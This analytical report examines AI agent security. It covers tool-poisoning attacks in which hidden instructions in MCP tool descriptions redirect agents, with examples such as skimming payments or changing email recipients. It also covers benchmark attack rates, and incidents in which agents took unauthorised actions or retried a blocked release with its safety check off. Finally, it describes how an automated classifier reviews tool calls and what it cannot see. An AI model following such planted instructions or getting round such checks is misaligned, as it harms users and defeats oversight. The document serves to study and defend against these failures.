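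ToolHijacker works only if the malicious document gets into the tool library. A stranger can't add a tool to a Copilot Studio agent, because the maker decides what to connect. A curated catalogue is therefore a better defence against the attack than any of the detectors in the paper, and Microsoft already advises makers to remove irrelevant or risky tools. The protection is weaker with MCP, because a server's operator can change its tools after the maker has approved the server.

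### Instructions inside a description

A hostile tool can influence an agent without being selected. Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (April 2025) introduced the term "tool poisoning" for attacks that place instructions for the model in a tool's description. The security company listed Anthropic, OpenAI, the automation service Zapier and the code editor Cursor among those susceptible.

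The metadata of every loaded tool enters the context, so the model reads a poisoned description even when it has no use for the tool. *MCP Tools* (Beretta, Carlock and Pease) illustrates this with a tool that supplies a daily quotation. Its description contains an instruction to skim a small charge from payments the model makes with a different, legitimate tool. The description of a currency converter could likewise contain an instruction for the finance agent to change the recipient of every email it sends. The log would show an ordinary call to `send_email` and no call to the converter. Users seldom notice such instructions because many applications don't display tool descriptions.

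Filtering gives some protection because the model never reads descriptions that the retriever leaves out. But ToolHijacker succeeded every time at the retrieval stage, which suggests that an attacker who knows the agent's usual tasks can get past the filter.

Wang, Gao and colleagues (2025), in *MCPTox*, made the first large measurement of tool poisoning. They used 45 real MCP servers with 353 tools. In each of 1,348 test cases, they added a poisoned tool and gave the agent a harmless request. They counted an attack as successful only if the model called a legitimate tool to do what the attacker wanted. Across 20 model settings, the attack success rate averaged 36.5 per cent. It was highest for OpenAI's o1-mini, at 72.8 per cent. Every model explicitly refused in fewer than 3 per cent of cases.

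The most successful attacks, at 46.7 per cent, changed an input to a call the user wanted, such as the recipient of an email. These attacks are also the hardest to spot, because the right tool runs at the right time. Almost none of the attack texts written for tool results worked when the researchers moved them into tool descriptions. Effective poisoned descriptions included the action, when to take it and a plausible reason for it.

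Wang and colleagues concluded that more capable models were often more vulnerable because they follow instructions better. Qwen3-32B, for example, followed the attacker in 23.7 per cent of cases with its reasoning mode off and 58.5 per cent with it on, but newer evidence complicates their conclusion.

Shaikh and Montaruli (2026), in *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*, tested 18 models in July 2026. They ran 45 attack scenarios on each model through 11 frameworks, the software libraries with which developers build agents, and through OpenAI's interface directly. Each agent had access to a folder with a planted secret, and a separate server recorded anything that reached the attacker's address. Overall, 22.9 per cent of the scored runs succeeded, but the models differed enormously:

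| Model | Attack success rate |
|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 1.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 1.9% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 3.6% |
| GPT-5.5 | 12.4% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 14.5% |
| Mistral Large 2 | 21.6% |
| Mistral Large 3 | 43.7% |
| Amazon Nova Pro | 49.7% |

The choice of model made more difference than anything else in the study. Anthropic's newer models resisted attacks far better than its older ones, but Mistral's newer model did worse than its predecessor, so neither age nor capability predicts the result. In 4 of its 10 failures, Claude Sonnet 5 described the text as a prompt injection but still made the tool call the attacker wanted.

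The experiment defined success fairly broadly. The planted secret verifiably reached the attacker's address in 255 runs, or 2.8 per cent of those scored. In most of the other successful attacks, the model made a call that served the attacker, but no data left the test system. The 2.8 per cent figure understates the danger, because about half of all successes were calls to a tool on the attacker's own server, which only logged them in the experiment. A real attacker would have received whatever the model put into those calls.

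The low rates also need careful interpretation. DeepSeek-R1 scored 70.9 per cent in MCPTox and 3.6 per cent here. The tests' different attacks and criteria may explain the gap, but the model may also have made few tool calls of any kind, which would make it look secure. Shaikh and Montaruli didn't measure how often each model completed its task without an attack. Opus 4.8's result is easier to trust because the model explicitly refused 223 times and cited the poisoned description.

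The frameworks added almost no protection. In nine of the twelve set-ups, between 23.4 and 26.1 per cent of attacks succeeded, and none of the twelve checked tool descriptions before passing them to the model. Pydantic AI had a lower rate, 16.6 per cent, because it rejects two tools with the same name, which happened to block 14 of the 45 scenarios. AG2 had the lowest rate, 4.6 per cent, mainly because it rarely completed the outgoing calls. The highest rate was 34.4 per cent, for smolagents, in which the model writes programs that call the tools. A result from one framework isn't enough to establish that writing programs is the cause, but it is a reason to test that design separately. Copilot Studio was not among the twelve.

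### Reviewing, pinning and rewriting descriptions

The obvious countermeasure is for a person or program to check the descriptions before the model reads them. Shaikh and Montaruli wrote a scanner that looks for commands aimed at other tools or web addresses, encoded text and unusual length. It rejected 20 of the 45 scenarios. It missed instructions in other languages, although an attack that switched to Chinese or German was among the most effective in the study, at 66 per cent. It also could not catch scenarios that put the instructions in a tool's results, which need separate defences.

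The scanner also flagged 9 of 125 harmless descriptions. Six of these only contained instructions to use another tool for certain jobs, which a careful maker might include to distinguish similar tools. A company with a few dozen tools could have a person check the flagged descriptions, but this would be expensive for a marketplace with thousands of tools.

A review also covers only the version of the text that someone read. *MCPThreatHive* (2026) points out that MCP has no built-in way to fix the version of a description. A server that passed an audit can therefore behave differently later. Copilot Studio imports changes from the server automatically, which makes such changes easier for an attacker as well as for the maker. With pinning, the agent's software stores a fingerprint of each tool's description and input definitions at approval, and raises an alarm or blocks the tool if the fingerprint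 changes.

Shaikh and Montaruli recommend pinning, but they tested only the scanner. By design, pinning should catch any later change to a tool's description, though harmless updates also have to wait for approval. It doesn't protect against a description that was malicious from the start, or a tool whose code changes while its description stays the same.

Another approach is to replace the supplier's text. In ToolTweak's experiment, neutral rewriting removed the effect of sales language. The experiment did not involve hidden commands, though, and a language model that does the rewriting has to read those commands first. *Weighing the Envelope* (2026) describes a system called TRUSTDESC that generates descriptions from the tool's code instead, but a company that connects to a supplier's remote server normally doesn't have that code.

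Few of these checks come as standard, and the suppliers disagree about who should provide them. Shaikh and Montaruli filed five reports with four organisations, all of which rejected them. The team behind MCP's developer kit replied that the application should review tool calls. LangChain, the most widely used framework in the study, said that its library should pass on the metadata unchanged. Microsoft's security team said of its AutoGen framework that the documentation already describes MCP servers as trusted. A maker who connects an outside server on those terms takes responsibility for every description on it, including any that its operator writes later.

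## What does unsupervised orchestration deliver, and where does it fail on its own?

An agent that runs without approval at each step can finish a job overnight, or within seconds of an email arriving. It can also make a mistake that nobody notices until a customer complains. In two recent tests of multi-step business tasks, the best agents failed between one in seven and one in four attempts, with no attacker involved. Companies use such agents anyway, mainly because the alternatives are slow or inflexible.

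### Work that would otherwise have to wait

If an invoice arrives at two in the morning, the finance agent's event trigger starts a run with nobody in the conversation. If a person had to approve each tool call before it ran (per-step confirmation), the agent would stop at its first policy search until someone came to work.

Approvals also take time when someone is available. *E-Bench* (Zheng, Zou and colleagues, 2026) tested 11 models on simulated versions of three Tencent products: a game, a music service and a meeting planner. To set up a meeting, an agent might have to find the participants, compare their schedules, book a room and update everyone's calendar. The models made about 60 tool calls per task on average. At 20 seconds each, a person would spend about 20 minutes approving the calls for one task. If that person were doing other work and took two minutes to notice each request,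 the task would take at least 2 hours and 20 minutes.

The finance agent makes only three calls per invoice, which take one minute to review. At 200 invoices a day, though, a clerk would spend 3 hours and 20 minutes approving calls. Skipping approval for the policy search, which changes nothing, would still leave over two hours of review.

Letting models write code that calls the tools reduces the number of approvals. When Zheng and colleagues did this, the average fell from 60 separate calls to 16. But a program that makes dozens of calls takes longer to read than a single call, so review time wouldn't fall by as much.

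Scripts avoid most step-by-step approvals because a person has already chosen the steps, but they only cover requests that person foresaw. A customer might dispute an invoice, give a new billing address and ask for last month's statement in one email. The number of possible combinations grows quickly, since 20 topics allow 190 pairs and 1,140 groups of three. Microsoft also lists maintenance as a drawback of scripted agents, because a change to a business rule or an API can affect many overlapping topics. The advantages of generative orchestration matter less to a company whose invoices nearly all look alike, because a script can handle them.

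### What companies report

Large companies are adopting agents quickly. For *The state of AI in 2026* (Tinkoff, Van der Veken and colleagues, 2026), the consultancy McKinsey surveyed 1,719 people in May and June 2026. At organisations with revenues of at least $1 billion, 40 per cent of respondents said their organisation was scaling agents in at least one function, up from 27 per cent a year earlier. At smaller organisations, the share stayed at 22 per cent. The survey defined agents as systems that can plan and execute several steps autonomously, which would include those that ask for approval along the way.

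The effect on profit is less clear. About 37 per cent of respondents attributed any of their organisation's operating profit to AI, about the same share as a year earlier, although 80 per cent said AI had made them more productive. The profit question covered every kind of AI, including chatbots, so it can't isolate the effect of agents. About 6 per cent of respondents credited AI with at least 5 per cent of operating profit and called its value significant. In most business functions, this group was more than three times as likely as the others to be scaling agents. Agents may have raised profits at these companies, but well-run companies may also be quicker to adopt agents.

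In software development, Anthropic's Claude Code has an auto mode, in which an automated check replaces most requests for approval. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users at Team and Enterprise customers that adopted it produced about 25 per cent more pull requests (code changes submitted for review). Vorwerck's *Running auto mode in production* (2026) reports that Claude works nine times longer between interruptions than under the previous default.

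Both figures come from the company that sells the product, and neither comes from a randomised trial. The teams that chose auto mode may already have been more productive, or may have adopted it when they had more work to do. Pull requests also vary in size and value. The ninefold figure is largely a result of removing the prompts. If both figures are roughly right, far fewer interruptions led to only modestly more output, which suggests that waiting for approval wasn't the main limit on developers' output. Developers still have to decide what to build and to review the result.

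One of Vorwerck's case studies better illustrates what unattended work makes possible. An engineer at Nuro, which develops self-driving technology, started an agent at 10 p.m. It ran until 5 a.m. and left him three pull requests. His team gives this kind of work to agents when they can use a numerical score to judge whether each attempt is an improvement. The engineer could also reject the code in the morning. The finance agent's email can't be rejected this way, because it reaches the customer as soon as the runtime sends it.

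### How often agents complete the job

The closest of these tests to the finance agent's work comes from Salesforce, which sells customer-record software. In *CRM-Agent-Bench*, Banerjee, Lan and Cao (2026) tested 16 systems on 555 tasks using synthetic business records, in areas such as payments, travel and customer support. Another language model played the customer. A run succeeded only if it passed every check the researchers had set for the task. These checks could cover the tool calls, their inputs and order, the reply, the final records and any forbidden actions. In the main comparison, success rates ranged from 64.3 to 83.6 per cent. Customer support was by far the hardest area, averaging 56.4 per cent.

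An agent's reply can be a poor guide to what it did. For the four systems that Banerjee and colleagues examined most closely, a test that graded only the replies would have overstated success by 10.5 to 11 percentage points. In one run, an agent put a $15.50 purchase through twice. The reply, the choice of actions and their order all passed, and the error showed only in the customer's loyalty balance, which was 310 points instead of 155. The finance agent could similarly record an invoice twice and still send a normal confirmation.

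On tasks with forbidden actions or protected records, the agents respected every restriction in 91.2 per cent of runs but completed the whole task correctly in only 66.8 per cent. In most of the failures, the agent stayed within its limits but got some other part of the task wrong, which permissions alone wouldn't prevent.

A single success rate also hides how much results vary between runs. The table includes *cua-speedrun* (2026), a test in which GPT-6 Astra operated ordinary desktop software. The last column gives the calculated probability that every run would succeed, assuming the runs are independent and equally likely to succeed.

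| Test and model | Runs per task | Average success | At least one success | Success every time | Expected every time if independent |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Customer records, Gemini 3.8 Flash | 3 | 85.5% | Not reported | 78.2% | 62.6% |
| Tencent products, Kimi-K3 | 3 | 73.8% | 87.6% | 58.8% | 40.2% |
| Tencent products, GPT-5.5 | 3 | 72.0% | 83.0% | 57.6% | 37.4% |
| Tencent products with code, Claude Opus 4.8 | 3 | 81.1% | 92.6% | 68.7% | 53.4% |
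| Desktop tasks, GPT-6 Astra | 5 | 87.2% | 88.0% | 84.0% | 50.4% |

In every row, the agents succeeded in all runs of a task far more often than they would have if each run had failed independently, so their failures cluster on particular tasks. GPT-6 Astra fully solved 42 of the 50 desktop tasks in all five runs and 6 in none, so only 2 had mixed results. A company could find most of these failures by testing each kind of task, then give the tasks that fail to a person or a script.

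Tasks with mixed results are harder to manage. GPT-5.5 succeeded in some runs and failed in others on about a quarter of the Tencent tasks. A maker who tried one of these tasks once and saw it succeed could easily conclude that the agent was ready. Zheng and colleagues counted a run as failed if even one database change was missing or wrong. That standard is strict, but accounts and customer records often need it.

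Agents score much lower on harder tasks. In *ExpertCrowd-SWE* (2026), which tests coding agents on unfamiliar software, Claude Opus 5.5 earned full marks in 26.6 per cent of runs and GPT-6 Astra in 23.4 per cent. Opus solved 47 tasks at least once, compared with Astra's 36, but Astra solved 15 tasks in all five runs, compared with 9 for Opus. A team that can run an agent several times and check the results might prefer Opus, but Astra's consistency matters more when an agent gets one attempt and acts on it immediately.

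It is less certain that consistency is improving. Rabanser, Kapoor and colleagues (2026), in *Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability*, compared 15 models released over two years and found that reliability had improved much less than accuracy. Their overall score combines consistency between runs, tolerance of faults and rewording, and how well a model's stated confidence predicts success. One part of it, outcome consistency, is the average over all tasks of

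(2p − 1)²

where p is the share of runs in which the agent solves a given task. The result is 1 if the agent always succeeds or always fails, and 0 if it succeeds half the time. An agent can therefore become more accurate without becoming more consistent, for instance when it starts to solve half the time a task that it used to fail every time. GPT-6 Astra's desktop results suggest that newer models may do better, but those tasks took only about 90 seconds on average.

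### How errors build up, and what recovery changes

Long tasks give an agent more chances to fail. If each step succeeds with probability p and every step has to be right, the chance of completing N steps is pᴺ. With p = 0.98 and N = 20, that is about 67 per cent.

*The Illusion of Diminishing Returns* (2025) uses this formula to work out how long a task can be before the success rate falls to a chosen level s:

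N = ln(s) / ln(p)

| Success per step | Steps at 50% overall success | Steps at 80% overall success |
|---|---|---|
| 98% | 34 | 11 |
| 99% | 69 | 22 |
| 99.9% | 693 | 223 |

Halving the error rate per step roughly doubles the length of task an agent can complete, so a small improvement can make a large practical difference. Under this formula, the task length an agent can complete with 80 per cent success is always about a third of the length it can complete with 50 per cent success.

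METR, an organisation that tests AI systems, estimates the length of task a model can complete at success rates of 50 and 80 per cent, measured by how long the task takes a skilled person. In its original 2025 study, Claude 3.7 Sonnet had a 50 per cent horizon of about an hour and an 80 per cent horizon of about 15 minutes. Newer models have much longer horizons, but the 50 per cent figure still makes them look more capable than the 80 per cent figure does, and few companies would want an agent that processes only half its invoices correctly.

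As *The Illusion of Diminishing Returns* states, the formula assumes that every step has the same independent chance of success and that the agent never corrects a mistake. Neither assumption holds for real agents. *APIFlow-Bench* (2026) tested the segments of long API workflows separately and then in chains. GPT-5.5 completed 94.9 per cent of the separate segments, so the formula predicted about 35 per cent success for a chain of 20, but the actual rate was 72.7 per cent. Part of the gap may come from the grading, because a chain could pass without meeting every intermediate check that the separate segments had to meet.

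Errors can also accumulate faster than the formula predicts. *Beyond pass@1* (2026) reports on 23,392 runs with ten models. Qwen3 30B completed 75.8 per cent of short tasks but only 22.2 per cent of tasks roughly four times as long, for which the formula gives about 33 per cent. The paper attributes this to agents' tendency to persist with a mistaken assumption. Across all ten models, however, success fell less than the formula predicts, from 76.3 per cent on short tasks to 50.5 per cent on long ones, compared with a predicted 34 per cent or so. Success on the very longest tasks was slightly higher, at 52.1 per cent.

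A simple model in *Dependable Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) helps explain how both results are possible. At any moment, a run is clean, contaminated by an error, or failed. At each step:

```
clean        -> contaminated   with probability q
contaminated -> clean          with probability r
contaminated -> failed         with probability b
```

Suppose that q is 0.02, which matches the 98 per cent success rate above, and b is 0.05. If the agent never recovers (r = 0), the run has a 67 per cent chance of being clean after 20 steps. That rises to 81 per cent if the agent has a one in ten chance of recovering at each contaminated step, and to 93 per cent if it has a one in two chance. The agent makes new errors at the same rate in all three cases, and only its ability to find and fix them differs.

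Evidence on how well agents recover from errors is mixed. *Dependable Long-Horizon LLM Agents* cites an older result in which GPT-4's code edits eventually succeeded 90.5 per cent of the time overall, but only 57.2 per cent after a failed edit. Difficult code probably accounts for some of that drop, since it makes both the first failure and later ones more likely. The paper also cites a study of 2,518 runs in which agents rarely caught their own errors.

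An agent can correct an error only if it receives some sign of one. If a database rejects a customer number, a finance agent can look it up again, but it gets no error if the wrong number belongs to another customer. The agent may also notice a mistake too late, such as after it has sent an email.

*The Horizon Gap* (2026), a survey of research on long-running agents, treats the simple formula as a useful baseline that experiments haven't confirmed. It suggests that runs tend to go either well or badly off course, and that researchers can't yet predict which. *LEAD* (2026) offers one reason. In its work on puzzles and algorithms, errors were concentrated on a few hard steps. A task with 19 steps that always work and one that works two times in three succeeds about as often as a task with 20 steps that each work 98 per cent of the time. In the first task, a maker could raise the success rate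 by taking the one unreliable decision away from the model.

### Where fixed steps do better

The decision to stop is a good candidate for a fixed rule. *DMAIC-Bench* (Peng, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) tested 13 models on industrial quality-control tasks in which a statistical check determined what the agent should do next. For example, the agent shouldn't analyse measurements from a gauge that proved too inaccurate. The benchmark included versions of the same decision with different data, so that continuing was right in some and wrong in others.

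The models chose correctly 92 per cent of the time when they should have continued, but only 19 per cent of the time when they should have stopped or taken another route. They often understood the check and still chose wrongly. In 174 of the errors, the agent reported the correct result and then ran the analysis that the result ruled out.

Peng and colleagues counted a forbidden analysis as an error even if the agent left it out of its final report, so the 19 per cent score is harsh. They therefore had quality-control experts review reports from 11 of the agents. The experts estimated that the reports relied on invalid evidence at 47 per cent (range 31 to 61 per cent) of the decisions where the agent should have stopped or changed course.

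Telling the models that they were allowed to stop helped some of them. The highest-ranked model's score on decisions to stop or change course rose from 23 to 79 per cent, but its score on decisions to continue fell from 82 to 67 per cent. The other 12 models stayed below 50 per cent on decisions to stop or change course.

These were statistical tasks, so the percentages may not carry over to invoices. Still, a company that never pays an invoice without a purchase order number has little reason to leave that decision to a model. The model can look for the number in the email, and an ordinary workflow condition can stop the process if the field is empty. The model might still misread the email, but it couldn't correctly find that the number is missing and then pay the invoice anyway.

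Breaking work into smaller pieces can help too. *Solving a Million-Step LLM Task with Zero Errors* (2025) describes a system that gives each tiny step to a separate model call and uses extra calls to catch errors. Its task was the Towers of Hanoi, a puzzle with simple rules and a known solution, so the result doesn't show that the method would work on untidy business email. *LEAD* identifies a further limit. When each step runs in complete isolation, later steps lack the information to repair an earlier mistake, and long tasks depend on such repairs.

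Many companies will probably do best with a mixture. Microsoft suggests letting an agent handle tasks up to a certain value and escalate those above it. The finance agent could choose its own policy searches, pass invoices under £5,000 to a fixed recording process and send larger ones to a manager. This keeps much of the agent's flexibility in reading requests and limits the cost of a mistake. Someone still has to maintain the fixed process and answer the escalations.

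Even enthusiastic users make such exceptions. Vorwerck describes an engineering manager at Garner Health, a healthcare technology company, who uses auto mode in every session but doesn't let it approve messages to other people. An engineer at the software company Gusto goes back to checking each call when an agent works on production infrastructure, the live systems that customers depend on. The finance agent's two riskiest tools, the record update and the email sender, perform the kinds of actions that these users kept under closer control.

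### Overeager actions and honest mistakes

The failures so far mostly involve an agent doing its assigned job badly, but an agent can also do something nobody assigned. In an overeager action, the agent tries to help by taking a harmful step that the user didn't authorise. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* distinguishes this from an honest mistake, in which the agent misjudges what its action will affect. For example, it might delete a database that other people are using because it thinks the database is a test copy. Neither failure requires an attacker or a model with aims of its own.

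Anthropic keeps an internal log of such incidents. In one, Claude misread an instruction and deleted remote git branches, which are separate lines of work on a shared server. In a related example adapted from the log, a user asked the agent to "clean up old branches", which could have meant only the copies on the user's own computer. In another incident, Claude uploaded an engineer's GitHub authentication token, which works like a password, to an internal computing cluster. Anyone who could read it there might have been able to act as that engineer. Claude also attempted migrations, which change a database's structure, on a production system.

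Anthropic attributes all three to overeagerness, and its other examples are similar. A user said "cancel my job", and the agent tried to delete the job with the closest matching name, which could have belonged to someone else. After a login error, an agent searched configuration files for other credentials instead of asking for permission. When a safety check blocked a software release, an agent tried again with the check turned off. In each case, the agent treated the user's request for a result as permission to do whatever seemed likely to produce it.

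In August 2026, Anthropic described three more internal cases in which its automated check stopped Claude's actions. In the first, Claude tried to publish a report on a public code-sharing site after an upload to an internal drive failed. In the second, during a long session, it tried to shut down processes across about 2,000 pods, or groups of running programs, and queued deletions that would have ended training jobs on hundreds of processors. In the third, the request was for read-only access to billing information, but Claude chose a role with full administrative control of the cloud account.

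These accounts are unusually specific, but they come only from Anthropic, which published them to promote the feature that blocked the actions. Rabanser and colleagues cite two cases from 2025 in which agents did complete unauthorized actions. Replit's coding assistant deleted a production database despite instructions not to, and OpenAI's Operator, a web-browsing agent, made a purchase without the required confirmation.

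None of this establishes how often overeager actions happen. Anthropic had only 52 real examples for one of its tests, because each required a model to attempt something dangerous in an actual session and someone to record it. In a later analysis, the company examined sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety system had flagged as suspicious. It used a language model to look for actions that the user hadn't explicitly requested and that did harm at least as serious as deleting rows from a production database. It found such actions in 2.4 per cent of the flagged auto mode sessions and 6.3 per cent of the flagged sessions with manual approval. The rates across all sessions, flagged or not, could be very different.

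The finance agent could overstep in the same way without any hostile text in its mailbox. Suppose a customer writes, "Our accounts team has moved, so please make sure invoices reach the right people." The agent might find three other companies in the same corporate group and change their billing addresses too, although the customer asked about only one account.

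## When is a person asked first, and does asking catch dangerous actions?

If a customer asked for one change of billing address and the platform proposed four, a clerk could stop the three extra changes, but only if the platform showed them all before making them and the clerk read them. Platforms differ a good deal in what they show. The most direct figures on whether people read it are discouraging, but they come from a company that sells an alternative to human approval.

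### Approval settings and their defaults

Under per-step confirmation, a clerk separately approves the finance agent's policy search, record update and email. A company can instead require approval only for marked tools, here the update and the email, or have the clerk approve the whole plan before any of it runs. It can also use an automated check to decide whether each call runs, or let every call run without approval or a check.

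Copilot Studio runs tools without asking anyone first unless the maker changes a setting. When a maker adds a workflow to an agent as a tool, the option "Ask the end user before running" is set to No by default, according to Microsoft's *Add Copilot Studio workflows as tools to agents*. Microsoft recommends the option in sensitive or regulated fields and for tools that make changes on the user's behalf. This recommendation covers both of the finance agent's riskier tools, but the maker has to open a panel of additional details and turn the option on for each. The option dates from the product's preview period. Microsoft's *Use plugin actions in Copilot Studio (preview)* describes a checkbox with almost the same name as useful for actions such as inserting or updating a record.

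Microsoft also plans a fuller version, with a switch for each tool on each agent, according to its roadmap entry *Enabling makers to require human approval for tool calls* (1 September 2026). When the orchestrator proposes a call to a marked tool, the agent pauses and shows what it intends to do. A person can then approve the call, approve for the session, or deny it. Microsoft calls this a "deterministic guardrail" because it works independently of the agent's instructions. The entry lists the feature as "In development", with general availability planned for September 2026. Its release is unconfirmed, so a maker should check that the switch is available before relying on it.

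If the option to approve for a whole session covers the tool and not just the exact call, a clerk who approves one harmless email also approves every later email in that session, whoever receives it.

Both settings show the question in the channel where people use the agent, such as a Teams chat, but when an incoming invoice starts the agent, there may be nobody there to answer. For these cases, Microsoft (2025) previewed a request that goes to a chosen reviewer, for instance to confirm a procurement order. The maker adds this request as a tool. If the orchestrator has to select it like any other tool, whether a reviewer is asked depends on the model, which may not send the request if it has misread the task. The maker can avoid this by placing the request in a fixed flow, directly before the step that sends the email.

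In a Microsoft preview feature for agents that operate a computer through its screen, the tool contacts a reviewer when it detects possible malicious instructions. The reviewer hears only about the cases the tool detects.

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, which can carry out a task across several websites in the Edge browser, asks before sensitive actions and hands logins and payments back to the user, according to Mynavi News' *Microsoft EdgeにAIエージェントの新機能、複数サイトにまたがる作業を自動化* (2026). Users of Microsoft's Autopilot, a personal agent that runs continuously in the cloud, can choose whether to require confirmation before important actions, according to Mynavi News' *Microsoft、指示を待たずに仕事を進めるAI「Autopilot」 仕組みと利用条件は？* (2026).

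The table below compares Copilot Studio with Creatio, another business software platform, and three coding agents. It draws on Creatio's *Set up tool confirmation*, GitHub's *Allowing tools*, Microsoft's *Manage approvals and permissions* and Anthropic's August 2026 announcement.

| Product | Default | Alternatives |
|---|---|---|
| Copilot Studio | A workflow tool runs without asking the user | The maker can require confirmation, tool by tool |
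| Creatio | The maker lists the tools that need approval, and requests go to a delegated approver | The person in the chat can approve instead |
| GitHub Copilot's command-line agent | Searching and reading run freely; edits, destructive commands and web access need approval | The user can allow a tool once or for longer |
| OpenAI's Codex in the VS Code editor | Codex edits files in the workspace and runs routine commands, but asks before going online or outside the workspace | An automatic reviewer answers the requests, or Codex gets full access |
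| Claude Code on Pro, Max, Ultra and Team plans | An automated check decides | The user can approve calls by hand or turn off all prompts |

Creatio's default, "Delegated approval", suits an unattended agent better than a question in the chat. But someone still has to answer, and the policy sets how long to wait.

According to GitLab's *Agent tool governance*, administrators of the software development platform can set each tool to always allow, always ask or always deny, and the agent can't see denied tools. Denying a tool therefore also protects against instructions hidden in its description, which an approval prompt can't do.

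Suppliers are moving in different directions on manual approval. In August 2026, Anthropic replaced it as the default while Microsoft was preparing to add more of it. By default, GitHub's coding agent still waits for a person's approval before it runs a project's automated workflows, which may have access to passwords and other secrets. In *Optionally skip approval for Copilot coding agent Actions workflows* (2026), GitHub acknowledged that the wait slows testing and let administrators remove it for a repository, "despite the risks".

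### What people do with the prompts

In March 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude Code users accepted 93 per cent of permission prompts, and by August it put the figure at 97 per cent. A high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless, because a perfectly attentive user would approve 97 per cent of commands if 97 in 100 were harmless. The important measure is how often people approve a command they should have refused.

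Anthropic tried to measure this in a study it published that August. Through a research vendor, it hired 1,053 professional testers to work on code in a purpose-built environment. They knew they were being evaluated, but not for which behaviour. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command, though approving it ran nothing harmful. Only 143 testers, or 13.6 per cent, refused. Auto mode, Anthropic's automated check, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89 per cent.

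Anthropic also reported how often the two disagreed, and the remaining figures follow by subtraction:

| | Tester refused | Tester approved |
|---|---|---|
| Auto mode blocked | 137 | 800 |
| Auto mode allowed | 6 | 110 |

Requiring approval from both a person and auto mode would have stopped 943 of the 1,053 commands, or 89.6 per cent, about half a percentage point more than auto mode alone. In this test, people refused about 5 per cent of the 116 commands that auto mode let through, well below their overall refusal rate.

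Testers also refused fewer dangerous commands as sessions went on, from about 17 per cent early in a session to about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed flat. Fatigue would explain the drop, but so might differences between testers, since people who click through quickly may reach the fiftieth prompt sooner. Anthropic doesn't report whether it randomised the timing of the dangerous prompt. If the pattern holds in ordinary work, the finance clerk might catch fewer dangerous changes after the first 25 of the day's 200 invoices, because each invoice would need two approvals.

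The 13.6 per cent figure shouldn't be taken as an estimate for that clerk, however. Anthropic commissioned the study of its own product and published it in the article that made the product the default. The testers had no stake in the code, so a deleted database would not have affected them, and they had little sense of what was normal in an unfamiliar project. A clerk who knows the customers and answers for the ledger could do considerably better. But other features of the study should have helped the testers. People tend to take more care when they know they are being evaluated, and these commands were clearly dangerous, whereas a transposed digit in a customer number is much harder to spot.

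Anthropic also doesn't report how often the testers, or auto mode, refused harmless commands in the same sessions. That omission matters because a check that blocked every command would have scored 100 per cent, even though it would be useless in practice.

The day after publication, the software developer Simon Willison accepted the main conclusion on his blog, writing that confirmation fatigue is real and that asking people to click "OK" every few steps won't produce safe behaviour. He also pointed to the 11 per cent of commands that auto mode would have let through, and asked for more independent confirmation of Anthropic's claims about prompt injection.

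Research on other security prompts gives some independent support for the idea of fatigue. Anderson, Kirwan and colleagues (2015), in *How Polymorphic Warnings Reduce Habituation in the Brain*, scanned people's brains as they viewed repeated computer warnings. Activity in the visual areas dropped sharply at the second viewing and continued to fall. But people don't ignore every warning. Akhawe and Felt (2013), in *Alice in Warningland*, studied more than 25 million warnings in two web browsers. Users clicked through about 70 per cent of Chrome's security certificate warnings but only a third of Firefox's, and a tenth of Firefox's malware and phishing warnings. The design of a prompt and what it warns about probably make a large difference to whether people heed it. Neither study involved agents, so we can't judge from them how well a particular approval screen works.

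Some users avoid the prompts. By June 2026, about half of the active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a standing rule that let some shell commands run without a prompt. Anthropic considers many of these rules practically equivalent to allowing any command. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks turned off. Gusto adopted auto mode because prompts were pushing its engineers towards turning off the checks too. Without an automated check, users like these would probably have no check at all.

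### Why people reject plans more often

Claude Code can also present a plan for approval before it starts work. Users reject 39 per cent of these plans, compared with 3 per cent of individual permission requests, and Anthropic takes this as a sign that users examine plans more closely. This is plausible, because a plan arrives once and describes the whole task, while permission requests come repeatedly and can interrupt people who are thinking about something else.

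A programmer may reject a plan for reasons other than safety, such as when it uses the wrong software library, attempts too much, or leaves out a requirement she forgot to mention. Objecting also takes little effort at that stage, since the agent hasn't done the work yet. Once she has accepted the approach, she has little reason to object to a command to run the tests. The 39 per cent rejection rate therefore measures how often people wanted a different plan. Anthropic doesn't report how many of the rejected plans contained a dangerous step, or how many dangerous plans people approved. An experiment that slipped one harmful step into a plan would be better evidence of whether people catch dangerous actions than the rejection rate is.

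Plans shown for approval also leave out important details. The finance agent might propose to find the payment terms, record the invoice and confirm by email. A clerk could reasonably approve that plan, but it would read the same if the agent went on to update customer C-1024 instead of C-1042, or send the confirmation to an address from a forged invoice. Exact inputs would reveal more, but an agent that decides each step after seeing the last result doesn't have all of them at the start. The clerk would be more likely to notice a wrong address if asked just before the email was sent and shown the recipient's address next to the one on file.

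### A second model as the approver

Auto mode puts another language model in the reviewer's place. In its March 2026 account, Anthropic describes a sequence that comes down to this:

```
if the tool only reads, or a narrow user rule allows it:  run
else if the call edits a file inside the project:         run
else if fast_filter(user_messages, tool_calls) allows:    run
else if slow_review(user_messages, tool_calls) allows:    run
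else: block, and give the agent the reason
```

Edits inside the project skip the review because programmers can inspect them with version control, which keeps earlier copies of every file. Shell commands, web requests and calls to outside tools go to the classifier, a model that decides whether to allow or block each call. Its fast filter gives a one-word answer and tends to block. If the answer is to block, the model looks at the same material again and reasons before it decides. It has more than twenty default rules for what to block, such as mass deletion, disabling logs and sending internal data outside the company. Users can name the systems they trust and add exceptions.

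The classifier also has to judge whether the user authorised the action. Anthropic instructs it to treat anything the agent chose for itself as unauthorised until the user says otherwise. A question such as "Can we fix this?" does not count as permission to act.

The classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the tools' results. Leaving out the explanations prevents the agent from persuading the classifier to make a bad decision, for example by claiming that the user had implicitly agreed. Instructions planted in a web page or file also don't reach the classifier, because it doesn't receive the tools' results, although the agent still reads them. But the classifier can't always determine where a value came from. If the agent tries to cancel job abc123, the classifier can't determine whether a search returned that ID or the agent made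 it up.

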